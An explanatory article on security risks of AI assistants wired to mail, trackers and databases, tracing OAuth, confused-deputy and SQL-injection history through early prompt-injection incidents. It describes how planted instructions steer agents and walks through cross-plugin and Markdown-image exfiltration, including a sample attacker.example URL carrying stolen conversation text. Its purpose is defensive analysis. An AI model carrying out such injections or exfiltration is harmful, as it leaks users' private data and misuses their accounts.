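# Security risks of AI systems connected to email, code, records and databases

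## What a connector is and what trust it inherits

A connector is software that lets an AI model read from or act in another service, such as a mailbox, a code host or a company database. Assistants such as Anthropic's Claude and OpenAI's ChatGPT use connectors to answer questions using people's own files and to do work in their accounts. Each connector gives the model a set of tools, each of which performs a single action, such as searching mail or deleting a file. An agent is an AI model that chooses and carries out a series of tool calls to finish a task. Most connectors now communicate with AI applications through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that Anthropic released in November 2024.

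Connectors usually act with the permissions of the person or company that installed them, which makes them useful but also creates the security problem. A mail service that receives a request from a connector can verify that the login is valid, but not whose words led to the request. An outsider whose text reaches the model, for instance in an email, may be able to steer what the connector does with those permissions.

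Suppose a user types "summarise my unread mail and update the project tracker" into an assistant with a connector for each service. Several systems handle the request before anything happens, and each checks something different.

### How the user's permissions reach the connector

A user gives the assistant access to her accounts through OAuth, the standard for granting an application access without handing over a password. Earlier applications asked for the password itself. *The OAuth 2.0 Authorization Framework* (Hardt, 2012) lists the problems with that: the application had to store the password, it gained far more access than it needed, and the user could cut it off only by changing the password, which cut off every other application too. OAuth replaces the password with an access token, a digital pass for one account.

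The standard defines four roles. In the mail example, the user is the "resource owner", the AI application is the "client", Google's sign-in system is the "authorization server" and Gmail is the "resource server". The application sends the user's browser to Google's sign-in page with a list of the permissions it wants. If she signs in there and approves, Google sends the browser back with a single-use code that should expire within ten minutes, and the application exchanges the code for an access token. The application may also get a refresh token, a longer-lived credential it can use to get new access tokens when old ones expire.

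The token's scope is its list of permissions. Google offers developers one scope for reading messages and settings, another for sending, a broader one for reading, composing and sending, and a full one that adds permanent deletion. Google's scopes are too coarse to limit an application to unread mail or mail from known senders, and none expires when the application finishes a summary.

Most such tokens are bearer tokens. In a companion to the main standard, *The OAuth 2.0 Authorization Framework*, Jones and Hardt (2012) define a bearer token as one that any holder can use in the same way as any other holder. Hardt notes that the main standard gives the receiving service no way to confirm that the application presenting a token is the one it was issued to.

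### Following the request

The AI application checks that the request comes from a logged-in session but, like any website, assumes that the person typing is the account's owner. It then combines its own standing instructions, the user's request and the tool descriptions into a text for the model. The tool descriptions cover what each tool does and when the model should call it.

The connector's maker writes those descriptions, and the model cannot check them against the code. Anthropic's *Gmail* page lists 24 tools for the Gmail connector in Claude's directory, including ones to search threads, send a message, move a message to the trash and create a filter. Anthropic warns there that it cannot verify that developers' tools "will work as intended or that they won't change". For this request, the model picks the search tool and asks for unread threads.

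The application, or a system attached to it, then adds the token, so the model never holds it. OpenAI's *App Security Whitepaper* (2026) explains that the company keeps credentials out of prompts to make it less likely that an attacker can trick the model into revealing them. According to Anthropic, Claude Tag, its assistant for Slack channels, uses a proxy at the edge of the model's working environment that checks most outgoing requests against a list of permitted destinations before attaching the credential. Both designs protect the credential from theft but do little to prevent its misuse, because the software attaches it to any permitted action the model picks.

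The mail service now checks that the token is valid, that it has not expired, and that its scope covers the request. Hardt lists these checks as duties of any resource server. If one fails, the service returns an error such as "invalid_token" or "insufficient_scope". Here all three pass, so the service returns the unread messages without checking whether the user wanted them.

The messages that come back contain outsiders' words. The connector passes them to the application, which adds them to the model's input, and the model writes its summary and works out what to change in the tracker. Trackers accept such changes. OpenAI's *Updated Box, Notion, Linear, and Dropbox apps* describes an update that added write actions, where the services support them, to ChatGPT apps including the one for Linear, a project tracker. The tracker runs the same three checks on its own token. If the model requests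 a later deadline, the tracker cannot determine whether the user wanted the change or it came from a stranger's email.

The user may get a chance to object before the assistant acts. ChatGPT asks for confirmation before it changes anything in an outside service, though OpenAI also describes settings that let administrators allow broader use. By default, Claude asks before it sends mail. In its Auto mode, it can take such actions without asking unless an automated check flags them, and Anthropic's *Use Google Workspace connectors* says that the check "can miss risky actions". When a confirmation does appear, it shows the user the proposed action, but she has to work out why the assistant is proposing it.

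In this example of inherited trust, the tracker accepts the change because the request carries the user's existing permissions, although no system has checked the request itself.

### Personal tokens and shared accounts

The example so far assumes a per-user token, which gives access only to what its user can access. Companies also connect assistants through a shared service account, which belongs to software rather than to a person. An administrator sets it up once, and many people use it.

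An application acting in its own name can reach far more data than one acting on a user's behalf. In Microsoft's example, an application that holds the Files.Read.All permission on behalf of a user called Tom can read every file Tom can already open, while one that holds it in its own name can read any file in the organisation. For mail, an administrator who consents to the second kind of access opens all users' mailboxes by default and has to limit it manually, according to Microsoft's migration guidance for Exchange. In *Understanding application-only access*, Microsoft advises developers never to use such access where a user would normally sign in to manage their own resources.

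Shared accounts are still useful when many people in a channel work with one assistant, because no single person's permissions are the obvious ones to use. Anthropic's *Agent identity in Claude Tag* argues that the assistant therefore needs its own accounts. Administrators also get a log that records every action under one known name. Anthropic lists another benefit, which is that what Claude can do in a channel "never changes based on who asked".

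That predictability is also the weakness, because if the company connects a shared Google account, anyone in a channel where the connector is on can ask Claude to read whatever the account can see. An employee who cannot open a finance folder can still ask Claude about it if someone has shared the folder with that account. The first such connector is on in every channel as soon as the administrator saves it. Anthropic's *Connect Google Drive, Calendar, and Gmail* tells administrators to create a dedicated account that starts with no access, and not to use their own.

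Some products fall between the two arrangements. For certain apps, OpenAI indexes a company's files with an administrator's credential, copies each file's permissions, and shows each user only what the copied permissions allow. The copy refreshes hourly, so a user may still see a file for a while after losing permission to it. Claude Tag can use a member's personal connector for that member's task in a shared channel. Anthropic has designed Claude to treat other people's posts in the thread as information for the task, not as instructions, but this safeguard depends on the model telling the two apart.

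### Instructions and data in one stream

Language models are bad at keeping a user's instructions apart from other text because they receive both as a single sequence of tokens, the word fragments into which software cuts text (unrelated to access tokens). When a model handles a user's mail, for example, the user's sentence and a stranger's email arrive as parts of the same text. Simon Willison, the programmer who coined the term "prompt injection" in 2022, writes in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025) that everything ends up glued together and the model cannot reliably rank instructions by where they came from.

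In SQL injection, an older and comparable attack, an attacker types database commands into a web form and the database runs them. Developers can prevent this with parameterised queries, which keep the command separate from the user's input so that the database never treats the input as a command. David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, argues in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* that language models have no equivalent fix, because a model only predicts the next token and makes no internal distinction between data and instructions. Developers can train a model to give some text priority, or mark passages as data, but these methods try to add a distinction that the underlying technology lacks. He thinks it quite possible that nobody will ever fully prevent prompt injection.

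Connectors expose a model to indirect prompt injection, in which an attacker hides instructions in content the model will read, and the model follows them as if its user had given them. David C gives the example of a job applicant who hides a line in a CV telling the recruiter's AI system to approve the candidate. Email makes the attack easier, since anyone can send a message to a known address. The sender needs no password or account with the assistant, and the user who asked for a summary may never open the message.

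A model does not follow hidden instructions every time. Its output varies from run to run, and one wording may fail where another succeeds. In *Pwning Agentic AI Part I*, Sean Park of TrendAI, a firm that sells security products, reports a test of 13 frontier models from Anthropic, OpenAI, Google and DeepSeek that used a doctored passport image. Hidden text in the image told a document-processing agent to leak other customers' records. The attack at least partly worked against models from nearly every vendor. Even a model that refuses nine times in ten gives poor protection, because an attacker can send ten emails.

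### The confused deputy

Computer scientists described the underlying pattern long before language models. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) recounts an accident from about eleven years earlier at Tymshare, which sold time on its computers. Customers could run a compiler, a program that translates source code, and name a file to receive its debugging output. The compiler also kept usage statistics in a file in its own directory, so the operators had given it permission to write to any file there. The billing records were in the same directory. A customer learned the name of the billing file and named it as the destination for debugging output. The operating system let the compiler overwrite the billing records because it had permission to write to that directory.

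Hardy rejects three obvious fixes. The compiler could refuse file names in other directories, but customers had good reasons to use those. It could refuse names in its own directory, but someone with proper access might want to write there. It could refuse the name of the billing file, but then programmers would have to change the compiler for each new sensitive file. Hardy concludes that the compiler "serves two masters", the customer and the operators. It carried authority from both and had no way to specify which authority it was using for a given file.

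In the mail request, the agent is the deputy. A stranger who writes to the user can only deliver a message, but the agent has the user's token. If the message names an action and the agent performs it, the stranger has acted with the user's authority, as the customer did with the compiler's. Like Tymshare's operating system, the mail service checks the permissions of the program making the request and finds them sufficient.

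Hardy's solution was the capability, a reference that both identifies a file and carries the right to write to it. The customer would give the compiler a capability for the debugging file, the operators would give it one for the statistics file, and the compiler would have no reason to use one in place of the other. He considered it poor design that one mechanism identified the file to the compiler and another gave it permission to write. OAuth tokens have the same split, because the token authorises sending mail while the model's text supplies the recipient.

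Capabilities would not solve this problem for an AI agent, however. Tymshare's programmers could find the line of code that wrote statistics and the line that wrote debugging output, and tie each to its own authority. David C calls a model an "inherently confusable deputy" because it has no such lines. He recommends a simple rule, from an online exchange between Willison and Baibhav Bista, that a model's privileges should drop to those of the party whose text it is processing. A strict version of the rule would make the mail example safe but prevent the assistant from doing its task. After reading a stranger's message, the assistant could do only what the stranger can do in the project tracker, which is nothing, so it could not make the updates the user wanted based on her mail.

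### The lethal trifecta

Willison offers a test that users can apply without understanding the model. An agent is open to data theft when it has access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate externally, a combination he calls the lethal trifecta. Moving private data out to an attacker, known as exfiltration, requires all three.

Suppose one of the unread messages contains instructions for the assistant to find password-reset emails and forward them to an outside address. The email connector alone provides all three parts of the trifecta: private data in the mailbox, untrusted content in the message, and the ability to forward mail.

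If the assistant worked only on a public enquiries inbox with nothing confidential in it, the attacker would gain nothing even if the planted message succeeded. If the private mailbox stayed connected but the assistant never read mail from strangers, the instruction would not reach it. OpenAI lets administrators impose roughly this limit by restricting email search to approved senders, but a stranger's message can still get through if an approved colleague forwards it. The remaining option is to stop the assistant from sending data out. The model might then still obey the message and collect the reset emails, but it could not pass them to the attacker.

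It is hard to block every route by which data can leave. In July 2026, Anthropic documented its Gmail connector as read-only, unable to create, send or modify mail. TechRadar's *I would rather use my own head than to let Claude reply* reported that the connector gained the ability to send mail the next month, which gave data a direct way out. Even with a read-only mail connector, data can leave through other tools. PromptArmor's *The Risks of Connectors in Your AI Applications*, from a firm that sells connector monitoring, points out that web browsing is an outbound channel because the receiving server can log every request. A search tool also transmits its query, which can contain stolen data. The three parts may come from different connectors. In PromptArmor's example, a customer's support ticket leads an agent to read an internal wiki page through one connector and post its contents as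 a public-facing reply through another.

The trifecta is a test for data theft. An attacker who wants to do damage needs only an assistant that reads untrusted text and has the power to change something. Park describes a hidden instruction in a support ticket that led an agent to encrypt every customer email address in a company database, using the database's own encryption functions and a key that only the attacker held. The company lost the use of the addresses, though no data had to leave its systems. In the mail example, a planted message could make the assistant close tasks in the tracker, move messages to the trash, or create a filter that goes on hiding mail after the conversation ends. PromptArmor therefore widens the third part of the trifecta from external communication to "downstream actions", which include changes to internal systems. Narrow scopes help somewhat. Google's scope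 for reading, composing and sending mail does not allow permanent deletion that bypasses the trash, so a user who notices in time can recover her messages.

### What a valid token leaves unanswered

A request's security context is the set of facts needed to judge it: who is making it, on whose behalf, for what task, whose text prompted it, and what limits apply. A valid access token establishes only some of these facts, and a shared account establishes fewer than a personal one.

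| Question | Per-user token | Shared service account |
|---|---|---|
| Who is asking? | In part. The token was issued to one application, but any holder can present it. | In part, for the same reason. |
| For whom? | Yes: the user who gave consent. | No. The service receives the shared account's identity, whoever made the request. |
| For what task? | No. | No. |
| Prompted by whose text? | No. | No. |
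| Within what limits? | In part. Scope and expiry set outer bounds, and so do the user's own permissions. | In part. The bounds are those of the shared account. |

Suppose a user asks an AI system to summarise their mail, and an email planted by a stranger prompts it to forward password resets. The forwarding request comes from the right application, acts for the right user and stays within its permitted scope. But forwarding password resets is not part of summarising mail, and the user did not write the text that prompted it. The mail service receives no information about what task the user set or who wrote that text.

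Companies can add some of the missing context by other means. OpenAI lets administrators restrict outgoing mail to approved domains, which is a tighter limit than any Gmail scope provides and would stop the forwarding regardless of what the model had read. In *Security & Privacy*, OpenAI also tells connector makers to assume that prompt injection will reach their servers. A server can check the values in a request, but a forwarding request looks the same whether the user or a stranger prompted it. The AI application is better placed to tell the difference because it received the user's sentence and the stranger's email separately before combining them, but a standard OAuth request has no field for passing that information on.

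## Before 2023: technologies that shipped before their security

Email, Office documents, web databases and OAuth all came into wide use before anyone had built checks against the abuse that followed. OAuth, for example, left users to judge which applications deserved access. Each gap stayed open for years, and the fixes that narrowed it worked in different ways. Security agencies now draw different lessons from this history when they write about connectors.

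### Email with no check on the sender

*Simple Mail Transfer Protocol* (Postel, 1982) defines SMTP, the protocol mail servers use to pass messages to one another. The sending machine identifies itself, states who the mail is from, names each recipient and transmits the text. The receiving machine replies "OK" at each step if it can accept the mail. It can refuse a recipient who has no mailbox there, but no step checks whether the mail really came from the stated sender. The design relied on machines on the network to give accurate information, which was reasonable when universities and research contractors ran most of them.

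Forging an email's sender took so little skill that nobody knows when it was first done. In a well-known early case in 1997, Joe Doll, who ran the web host joes.com, closed a spammer's account, and the spammer retaliated by sending advertising that appeared to come from Doll. In *SMTP*, a later edition of the standard, Klensin (2008) called mail "inherently insecure" because even fairly casual users could make a message seem to come from somewhere else. He still opposed forcing people to send only from their own addresses, since that would break legitimate uses such as sending mail on someone else's behalf. He thought real security required digital signatures on the messages themselves.

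Engineers added three checks alongside SMTP. The Sender Policy Framework (SPF) lets a domain's owner list the servers allowed to send its mail. Wong and Schlitt (2006) published it as an experiment in *Sender Policy Framework (SPF) for Authorizing Use of Domains in E-Mail*. DomainKeys Identified Mail (DKIM) followed in 2007 and attaches a digital signature that the receiving server can verify. The third, DMARC, dates from 2015 and checks that the domain that passed SPF or DKIM matches the one in the "From" line. It also lets the domain's owner advise receivers to deliver failing mail, mark it as spam or reject it, as SIDN's *DMARC is now a formal internet standard for e-mail security* explains. DMARC began as an informational document and became a Proposed Standard only in May 2026, according to the RFC Editor's *Domain-Based Message Authentication, Reporting, and Conformance (DMARC)* (2026).

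All three were voluntary, so forgers could keep using the names of domains whose owners had not adopted them. In 2022, Google started requiring some form of authentication for mail to Gmail, and Kumaran (2023) reported in *New Gmail protections for a safer, less spammy inbox* that unauthenticated messages to Gmail users then fell by 75%. From February 2024, 42 years after Postel's standard, Google and Yahoo also required bulk senders to authenticate their mail. Google defines a bulk sender as anyone who sends more than 5,000 messages to Gmail addresses in a day, and its *Email sender guidelines FAQ* describes slowing down bulk mail that fails SPF. In *Google stats show why DMARC and email authentication matter*, Valimail, which sells email authentication, cites Google's figure of 265 billion fewer unauthenticated messages in 2024.

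These checks only slightly protect an AI assistant that reads mail. A criminal can register a new domain, set up SPF, DKIM and DMARC correctly, and pass all three. Passing confirms which domain sent the message but doesn't establish whether a model can safely act on the text.

### Documents that carry programs

Microsoft Word for Windows has had a macro language since its first version in 1989. A macro is a small program that automates work in a document, and some macros run as soon as the user opens the file. Microsoft designed macros on the assumption that documents came from people whose programs the user would want to run.

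Concept, the first macro virus to spread widely, appeared in 1995. When a user opened an infected document, the virus copied itself into Word's global template and from there into other documents the user saved. It did little else. Melissa, in March 1999, also emailed itself to the first 50 entries in the victim's Outlook address book. The message came from the real account of someone the recipients knew, and many opened the attachment.

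Microsoft at first let users decide whether to run macros. Word 97 warned that a document contained macros and offered to enable them, and Office 2007 disabled most macros but let users enable them in one or two clicks. Attackers responded with documents that told readers to enable the content. In February 2022 Microsoft announced that Office would block macros in files from the internet by default. It paused the change in early July after customers complained and resumed it later that month, 27 years after the Concept macro virus appeared.

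Office's macro block relies on a mark that Windows attaches to files from the internet. Office does not run macros in a marked file, and it shows a warning with no button to enable them. A user can still remove the mark in the file's properties, and an administrator can exempt trusted locations. Macros that do run can do everything they could before. Attackers soon turned to disk-image files, because Windows did not always pass the mark on to the documents inside.

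Of the four cases, this one looks most like indirect prompt injection. In both, a stranger's document contains instructions that take effect with the reader's permissions. But the mark records where the content came from, and a connector's request has no such record. Office also stores macros separately from the document's text, so it can switch them off and still display the page. An instruction hidden in an email is part of the ordinary text, so an assistant that must read the email can't switch it off in the same way.

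### Text that becomes a command

Jeff Forristal, writing as "rain.forest.puppy", published the first description of SQL injection in the hacker magazine *Phrack* in December 1998. Web developers had been building database commands by joining their own text to whatever a visitor typed into a form, assuming the visitor would type the kind of value the form asked for.

Even an innocent name shows how this fails:

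```python
name = "O'Brien"   # typed into a web form

# Unsafe: the name becomes part of the command
db.execute("SELECT * FROM customers WHERE name = '" + name + "'")

# Safe: the command is fixed and the name travels separately
db.execute("SELECT * FROM customers WHERE name = ?", (name,))
```

In the unsafe version, the apostrophe in O'Brien ends the quoted text early, so the database reads "Brien" as part of the command and returns an error. An attacker would follow the apostrophe with words that form a valid command, and the database would run it. The safe version is a parameterised query. The database works out the structure of the command with a question mark in place of the name and only then fills in the name, so nothing in the name, including the apostrophe, can alter the command.

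MySQL, the database behind many early websites, gained this feature in 2004, and some other databases had it earlier, but developers were slow to use it. In March 2024, the US cybersecurity agency CISA and the FBI noted in a joint alert, *Malicious Cyber Actors Use SQL Injection Vulnerabilities to Compromise Systems*, that others had called SQL injection flaws "unforgivable" since at least 2007. They were responding to a 2023 campaign in which the criminal group Cl0p exploited SQL injection in MOVEit, a file-transfer product for companies. The attacks affected 2,769 organisations and almost 95 million people, according to figures from the security vendor Emsisoft in Security Boulevard's *CISA, FBI Push Software Developers to Eliminate SQL Injection Flaws* (2024).

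CISA and the FBI call SQL injection "still a prevalent class of vulnerability", while David C of the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) describes it as now rare in websites. The assessments differ partly because they cover different software. David C credits better defaults, and modern web frameworks usually parameterise queries automatically. The agencies were writing about commercial software, where one careless line in a widely used product can expose thousands of customers. They therefore want manufacturers to use libraries that make the safe method the default, and to check for unsafe queries whenever a programmer submits new code.

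They also warn against relying on input sanitisation, which means removing dangerous characters before they reach the database. It stops some attacks, but attackers can often get around it and large companies struggle to apply it everywhere. David C objects similarly to filters that block known prompt-injection phrases, because an attacker can reword an instruction in endless ways. Unlike developers defending against prompt injection, database developers can use parameterised queries instead of filtering.

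### Consent to the wrong application

OAuth first appeared in 2007. Its consent page shows the name of the application asking for permission. The developer supplies that name when registering the application, and users tended to assume that someone had checked it.

In *Phishing with Client Application Name Spoofing*, DeMarre (2012) returned to a warning he had first sent to OAuth's working group in October 2011. A malicious developer could register an application as "Google, Inc." with some other service, whose genuine consent page would then show users a request for access from Google. Checking the page's address, the usual advice against phishing, would not help because the address would be correct. He also predicted that on a social network such an application could spread like a worm by posting links from its victims' accounts. He suggested that consent pages put "an application calling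 itself" before the name.

The espionage group Pawn Storm was using the technique by 2015. *Pawn Storm Abuses Open Authentication*, from the security vendor Trend Micro, describes how the group emailed prominent Gmail users a fake security notice inviting them to install "Google Defender". The link led to a real Google page, where clicking "Allow" gave the group a token that let it access the mailbox until the user or Google revoked it. Yahoo users received a similar offer of "McAfee Email Protection" in late 2015.

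In May 2017, a worm spread through fake Google Docs invitations. Each appeared to come from one of the victim's contacts and linked to an access request from an application posing as Google Docs. If the victim agreed, the application sent the same invitation to the victim's contacts. Google's *Protecting you against phishing* (2017) reports that the company stopped the campaign within an hour and that it affected fewer than 0.1% of users. That was close to a million people, according to IBTimes UK's *Google was warned of Google Docs phishing technique 6 years ago*. The article also reports that DeMarre, a security researcher, said he had warned Google of the technique in 2012 and received a "modest bounty".

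Google revoked the access that victims had granted and removed the fake applications. By July 2017 it also required some new web applications to pass verification before launch and showed users of unverified ones an error page. That month, according to Google's *New security protections to reduce risk* (2017), the company replaced the error page with an "unverified app" warning that users could click past. From 8 July 2019, Google blocked new installations of unverified applications that read Gmail data in company accounts, unless an administrator had chosen to trust them. People who had already installed such an application kept it.

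Verification is meant to catch dishonest applications. The makers of AI assistants can pass it honestly, because the user does want the assistant to read her mail. The deception comes later, in a message the assistant reads, and the consent page does nothing to prevent it.

### Changing the default and changing the structure

Some of these fixes changed a system's structure so that it separated things it had previously mixed, such as database commands and values. Others changed a default, so that people who made no decision got the safer behaviour.

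| | Email | Office macros | SQL injection | OAuth consent |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Feature | SMTP, 1982 | Word's macro language, 1989 | Web forms that query databases, mid-1990s | OAuth 1.0, 2007 |
| Trust assumed | The sending machine states the true sender | The reader wants to run the author's programs | Visitors type only the value the form asks for | An application's name shows who made it |
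| Early abuse | Spam forged in Joe Doll's name, 1997 | Concept, 1995 | Public description, 1998 | Pawn Storm, 2015 |
| Change of structure | SPF, 2006; DKIM, 2007; DMARC, 2015 | None | Parameterised queries, in MySQL from 2004 | None |
| Change of default | Google and Yahoo's bulk-sender rules, 2024 | Block on macros in files from the internet, 2022 | Gradual, through frameworks and libraries | Block on unverified apps that read company Gmail, 2019 |
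| Years from early abuse to fix | 27, to the 2024 rules | 27 | 6, to MySQL's parameterised queries | 4 |

The six-year figure for SQL injection is misleading on its own. Developers had a way to prevent the attack by 2004 at the latest, but Cl0p's campaign came 19 years later because the safe method was still optional. Email had a similar delay between having a fix and requiring it. SPF existed for 16 years before Gmail required any authentication, and the 75% fall came only after that requirement.

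Google moved fastest on OAuth, where it ran both the consent page and the mailboxes. Microsoft also controlled its own product, but its customers had built office work on macros for years, and their complaints interrupted even the 2022 change. The few companies that run the most popular assistants could change a connector default in a single release, for example by having the assistant ask before it sends mail, but the longer they wait, the more work customers will have built on the old behaviour.

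The delays in these four cases don't predict what will happen with connectors, because all four are notorious failures. Many other technologies shipped with weak security and never suffered an attack like Melissa. The cases are more useful for working out which parts of the connector problem have a known kind of fix.

### Where the early-web comparison fits

The US National Security Agency's guidance, *Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2026), compares MCP to early web protocols because both came out with a "flexible and underspecified design" that left safe use to whoever implemented them. Adoption then outpaced the security model.

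The details support the comparison well. The agency found that the protocol does not define how to tie a session to an identity, and that many implementations leave out authentication entirely. Those that include it often do not distinguish between users who may read records and users who may delete them. MCP relies on bearer tokens but does not require developers to make them expire or to support cancelling them. A server that a user has already approved can often gain new abilities without further approval. Many implementations also keep poor logs or none. Postel's mail servers had the same problem with identity in 1982, when they accepted whatever name the sending machine gave.

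Web developers already know how to handle most of these problems. The NSA recommends familiar tools such as signed messages with expiry times, outgoing connections limited to approved destinations, and logs that record who called which tool with what values. MCP's maintainers also added authorization rules between March 2025 and July 2026. These measures can establish who is making a request, for whom, and within what limits.

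Authenticating a request cannot establish whose text prompted it. If a planted email steers an agent into forwarding password resets, the agent can still sign the request correctly, with a fresh token and a log entry, and the connector will accept it. DMARC has the same limit. It confirms which domain sent a message, but the reader still has to judge the contents.

The NSA argues that agents bring risks that established defences do not adequately address, such as calling new tools while running and accepting one another's output without checking it. In its travel example, one assistant links a request to an earlier email about holiday plans, while another treats the same request as new. An attacker can exploit that variation by preparing the context in advance. The agency wants developers to treat every output from a tool or model as untrusted input to the next step and scan it for hidden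 instructions. Scanning has the same weakness as sanitising database input, because an attacker can always try another wording.

### Where the SQL comparison breaks down

David C wrote his December 2025 article because he had noticed experienced web security professionals treating prompt injection as a new form of SQL injection. He considers this dangerous because someone who believes it will expect an equivalent of the parameterised query, or buy a product sold as one, and will give the system more access than it should have.

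David C bases his argument on the lack of a boundary between instructions and data inside a model. Once a developer has separated commands from values, a database enforces the separation, but a model reads a label marking a stranger's email as data as more text. He concludes that owners should treat prompt injection as a risk that remains after every precaution. They should assume that an attacker who can feed text to the model can use any tool the model can use. If they cannot accept the consequences, a language model may be the wrong choice.

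One objection is that parameterised queries work by letting developers keep data separate from commands, not by making it safe to join them. Perhaps developers can do something similar around a model by keeping untrusted text away from the part of the system that chooses actions. Researchers proposed several such designs in 2025 and 2026. David C cites two of them with approval and recommends safeguards that do not depend on a model's judgement. His claim about the model itself is hard to dispute, and it does not rule out boundaries in the software around it.

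The comparison with SQL injection does hold for the connector's own code. A connector is ordinary software, and if it pastes a value from the model into a database command, it has the flaw Forristal described in 1998. The NSA reports cases in which attackers ran arbitrary commands because connectors passed on such values unchecked. Parameterised queries completely prevent the database version of this flaw, but they don't help when a tool lets the model write the whole database command, as some database connectors do. If a planted message has shaped that command, the database will still run it as long as the account's permissions allow it.

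David C accepts one part of the comparison between SQL injection and prompt injection, the history of adoption. By his account, SQL injection attacks peaked around 2010, when many websites relied on databases but few of them had dealt with the risk. Defaults improved after a decade of break-ins. He warns that a similar wave of breaches may follow if companies put language models into most of their applications without designing for prompt injection.

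## 2022 to 2024: the first plug-ins and mail assistants

On 11 September 2022, Riley Goodside posted experiments with GPT-3, OpenAI's language model at the time. He asked it to translate a sentence into French, but the sentence contained an instruction to ignore the request and output a taunt. GPT-3 output the taunt, and did so again when he warned it that the text might contain tricks.

The next day, in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3* (2022), Willison proposed calling the weakness "prompt injection". Developers were already selling products that joined their own instructions to whatever a customer typed, and he compared this to SQL injection. He hoped OpenAI would let developers send instructions and data separately, as a parameterised query does. A reader pointed out that one OpenAI model already accepted them separately and still followed instructions in the data. Four days after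 the first post, in *I don't know how to solve prompt injection* (2022), Willison wrote that he had "no idea how to reliably beat" it. By April 2023 he thought that separating instructions from data might be impossible with the models then available.

The first attacks mostly embarrassed their victims. A recruitment startup released a Twitter bot that used GPT-3 to answer posts about remote work, and users soon got it to threaten to overthrow the president. The attackers had to write to the bot directly, and it could only post text.

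### Planting instructions where a model will read them

*Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) introduced the term "indirect prompt injection". It describes how an attacker could plant instructions in a web page, a code package or an email. The planted text could be short, because it could tell the model to fetch longer instructions from elsewhere.

The team first built a mock assistant on OpenAI's models, with tools for searching the web, reading and sending mail, reading an address book and keeping notes. Every tool returned prepared content, so nothing reached a real account. In one test, instructions in an email led the assistant to look up the user's contacts and send them the same instructions, which other assistants could then read. In another, the assistant saved part of the attack in its notes. After a reset, it behaved normally until the user asked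 it to read the notes, and then it followed the attack's instructions again.

The February version of the paper covered only mock applications, according to the abstract that Schneier (2023) reproduced in *Prompt Injection Attacks on Large Language Models*. By 1 March the team had also published an attack on Bing Chat, Microsoft's search chatbot, which could read the page open in the user's browser. To avoid exposing other users, they hid instructions in a page on their own computer. The instructions directed the chatbot to learn the user's real name without raising suspicion, but didn't suggest how. One researcher posed as a journalist and asked about the weather. Bing Chat asked what he did for a living and whether he wrote under his own name, and later offered him a link with the name encoded in it.

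Bing Chat ended a session if the user typed a known jailbreak, which is text designed to get around a model's restrictions. The same text worked when Bing Chat read it on a web page. Microsoft seems to have filtered what users typed without considering the other text the model read.

The study showed that these attacks were possible but gave no success rates. The researchers reported only that their instructions often worked on the first attempt, even with spelling mistakes. Attacks on GitHub Copilot, which suggests code, were much less effective inside larger programs. The researchers had no access to Microsoft 365 Copilot or ChatGPT's new plug-ins, which would soon connect models to people's real mail.

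### Plug-ins that could set off other plug-ins

OpenAI announced plug-ins on 23 March 2023. A plug-in let ChatGPT call another company's service, much as a connector does now. The model decided when to call the service based on the developer's description. Expedia, Slack and Zapier were among the first dozen partners.

OpenAI's *ChatGPT plugins* reports that by launch, the company's testers had found ways for plug-ins without safeguards to carry out prompt injection and send fraudulent mail. OpenAI limited its own browsing plug-in to fetching pages, so the model could not submit forms, and acknowledged that this reduced the risk but did not remove it.

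In April, Willison wrote in *Prompt injection* that what worried him most was the growing number of ways to combine plug-ins. Johann Rehberger, a security researcher who writes the blog Embrace the Red, soon had an example. He noticed that text on a web page could make ChatGPT search for flights through the Expedia plug-in, which was harmless enough. He then looked for a plug-in with access to something private and found Zapier's, which could read a user's mail. In May 2023 he demonstrated this attack, explained in Embrace the Red's *ChatGPT Plugin Exploit Explained*:

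1. A user asks ChatGPT to read a web page through WebPilot, a browsing plug-in.
2. Text on the page tells ChatGPT to find the user's latest email.
3. ChatGPT calls the Zapier plug-in, which the user has authorised to read her mail.
4. ChatGPT summarises the email in 20 words and adds the summary to a web address on the attacker's server.
5. ChatGPT asks WebPilot to open that address, and the server receives the summary.

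Neither plug-in malfunctioned, but ChatGPT acted as a confused deputy between them. Rehberger named the attack "cross-plugin request forgery" after an older attack in which one website makes a visitor's browser send commands to another site.

Zapier responded by requiring users to confirm such actions through an authenticated step. Without authentication, an attacker could have told ChatGPT to follow the confirmation link. The change protected only Zapier's users. In Embrace the Red's *Plugin Vulnerabilities*, Rehberger showed that a web page could use a different plug-in, Chat with Code, to make a user's private GitHub repositories public. He wanted OpenAI to stop plug-ins from triggering other plug-ins by default. OpenAI has since retired plug-ins.

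### How an image address carries data out

An attacker could also steal a conversation without a second plug-in, because the chat window itself would send the data. Chatbots format their answers in Markdown, a simple notation in which a line of text can stand for an image at a web address. The theft works like this:

1. A planted instruction tells the model to include an image in its answer and to put a summary of the conversation in the image's address.
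2. The model writes an address such as `https://attacker.example/logo.png?q=moving+to+Leeds+in+May`.
3. The chat window treats this as an ordinary image, and the user's browser requests it immediately.
4. The attacker's server records the whole address, including the words after the question mark.

The user does not have to click anything, and the server does not have to return a picture. Roman Samoilenko found the problem in ChatGPT in late March 2023, and Rehberger found it independently a few days later. When Rehberger reported it, OpenAI told him that displaying such images was a feature and that it planned no changes, according to his post *ChatGPT Plugins*.

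Microsoft treated the same problem in Bing Chat as a flaw. The company added a Content Security Policy, a list that tells the browser which sites a page may load images from, according to Embrace the Red's *Bing Chat*. The list contained four Microsoft addresses. The browser enforces it whatever the model writes, so the protection does not depend on the model recognising an attack.

Attackers can still use a permitted site to collect stolen data if the site is open to outsiders. In September 2023, Google gave its chatbot Bard access to users' Gmail, Drive and Docs. Google already had a list of permitted image sites, but the list allowed any address under google.com, where anyone can run small programs through Google's Apps Script service. In Embrace the Red's *Hacking Google Bard*, Rehberger describes writing a program there that saved incoming text to his own document. He then used instructions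 in a Google Doc to make Bard send the user's conversation to the program. In January 2026, Willison reported the same kind of gap in the mail assistant Superhuman, whose list allowed the site that hosts Google Forms.

Anthropic instead made Claude users click before an image would load, according to Embrace the Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*. OpenAI did not act until December 2023, when ChatGPT's web version began checking with an OpenAI server whether each image address was safe. OpenAI did not publish the criteria. Rehberger tried a separate address for each of the 36 letters and digits, and nine passed the check. An attacker could still leak some text one character at a time, according to Embrace the Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*.

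| Product | Time from report to fix | Vendor's response | What remained |
|---|---|---|---|
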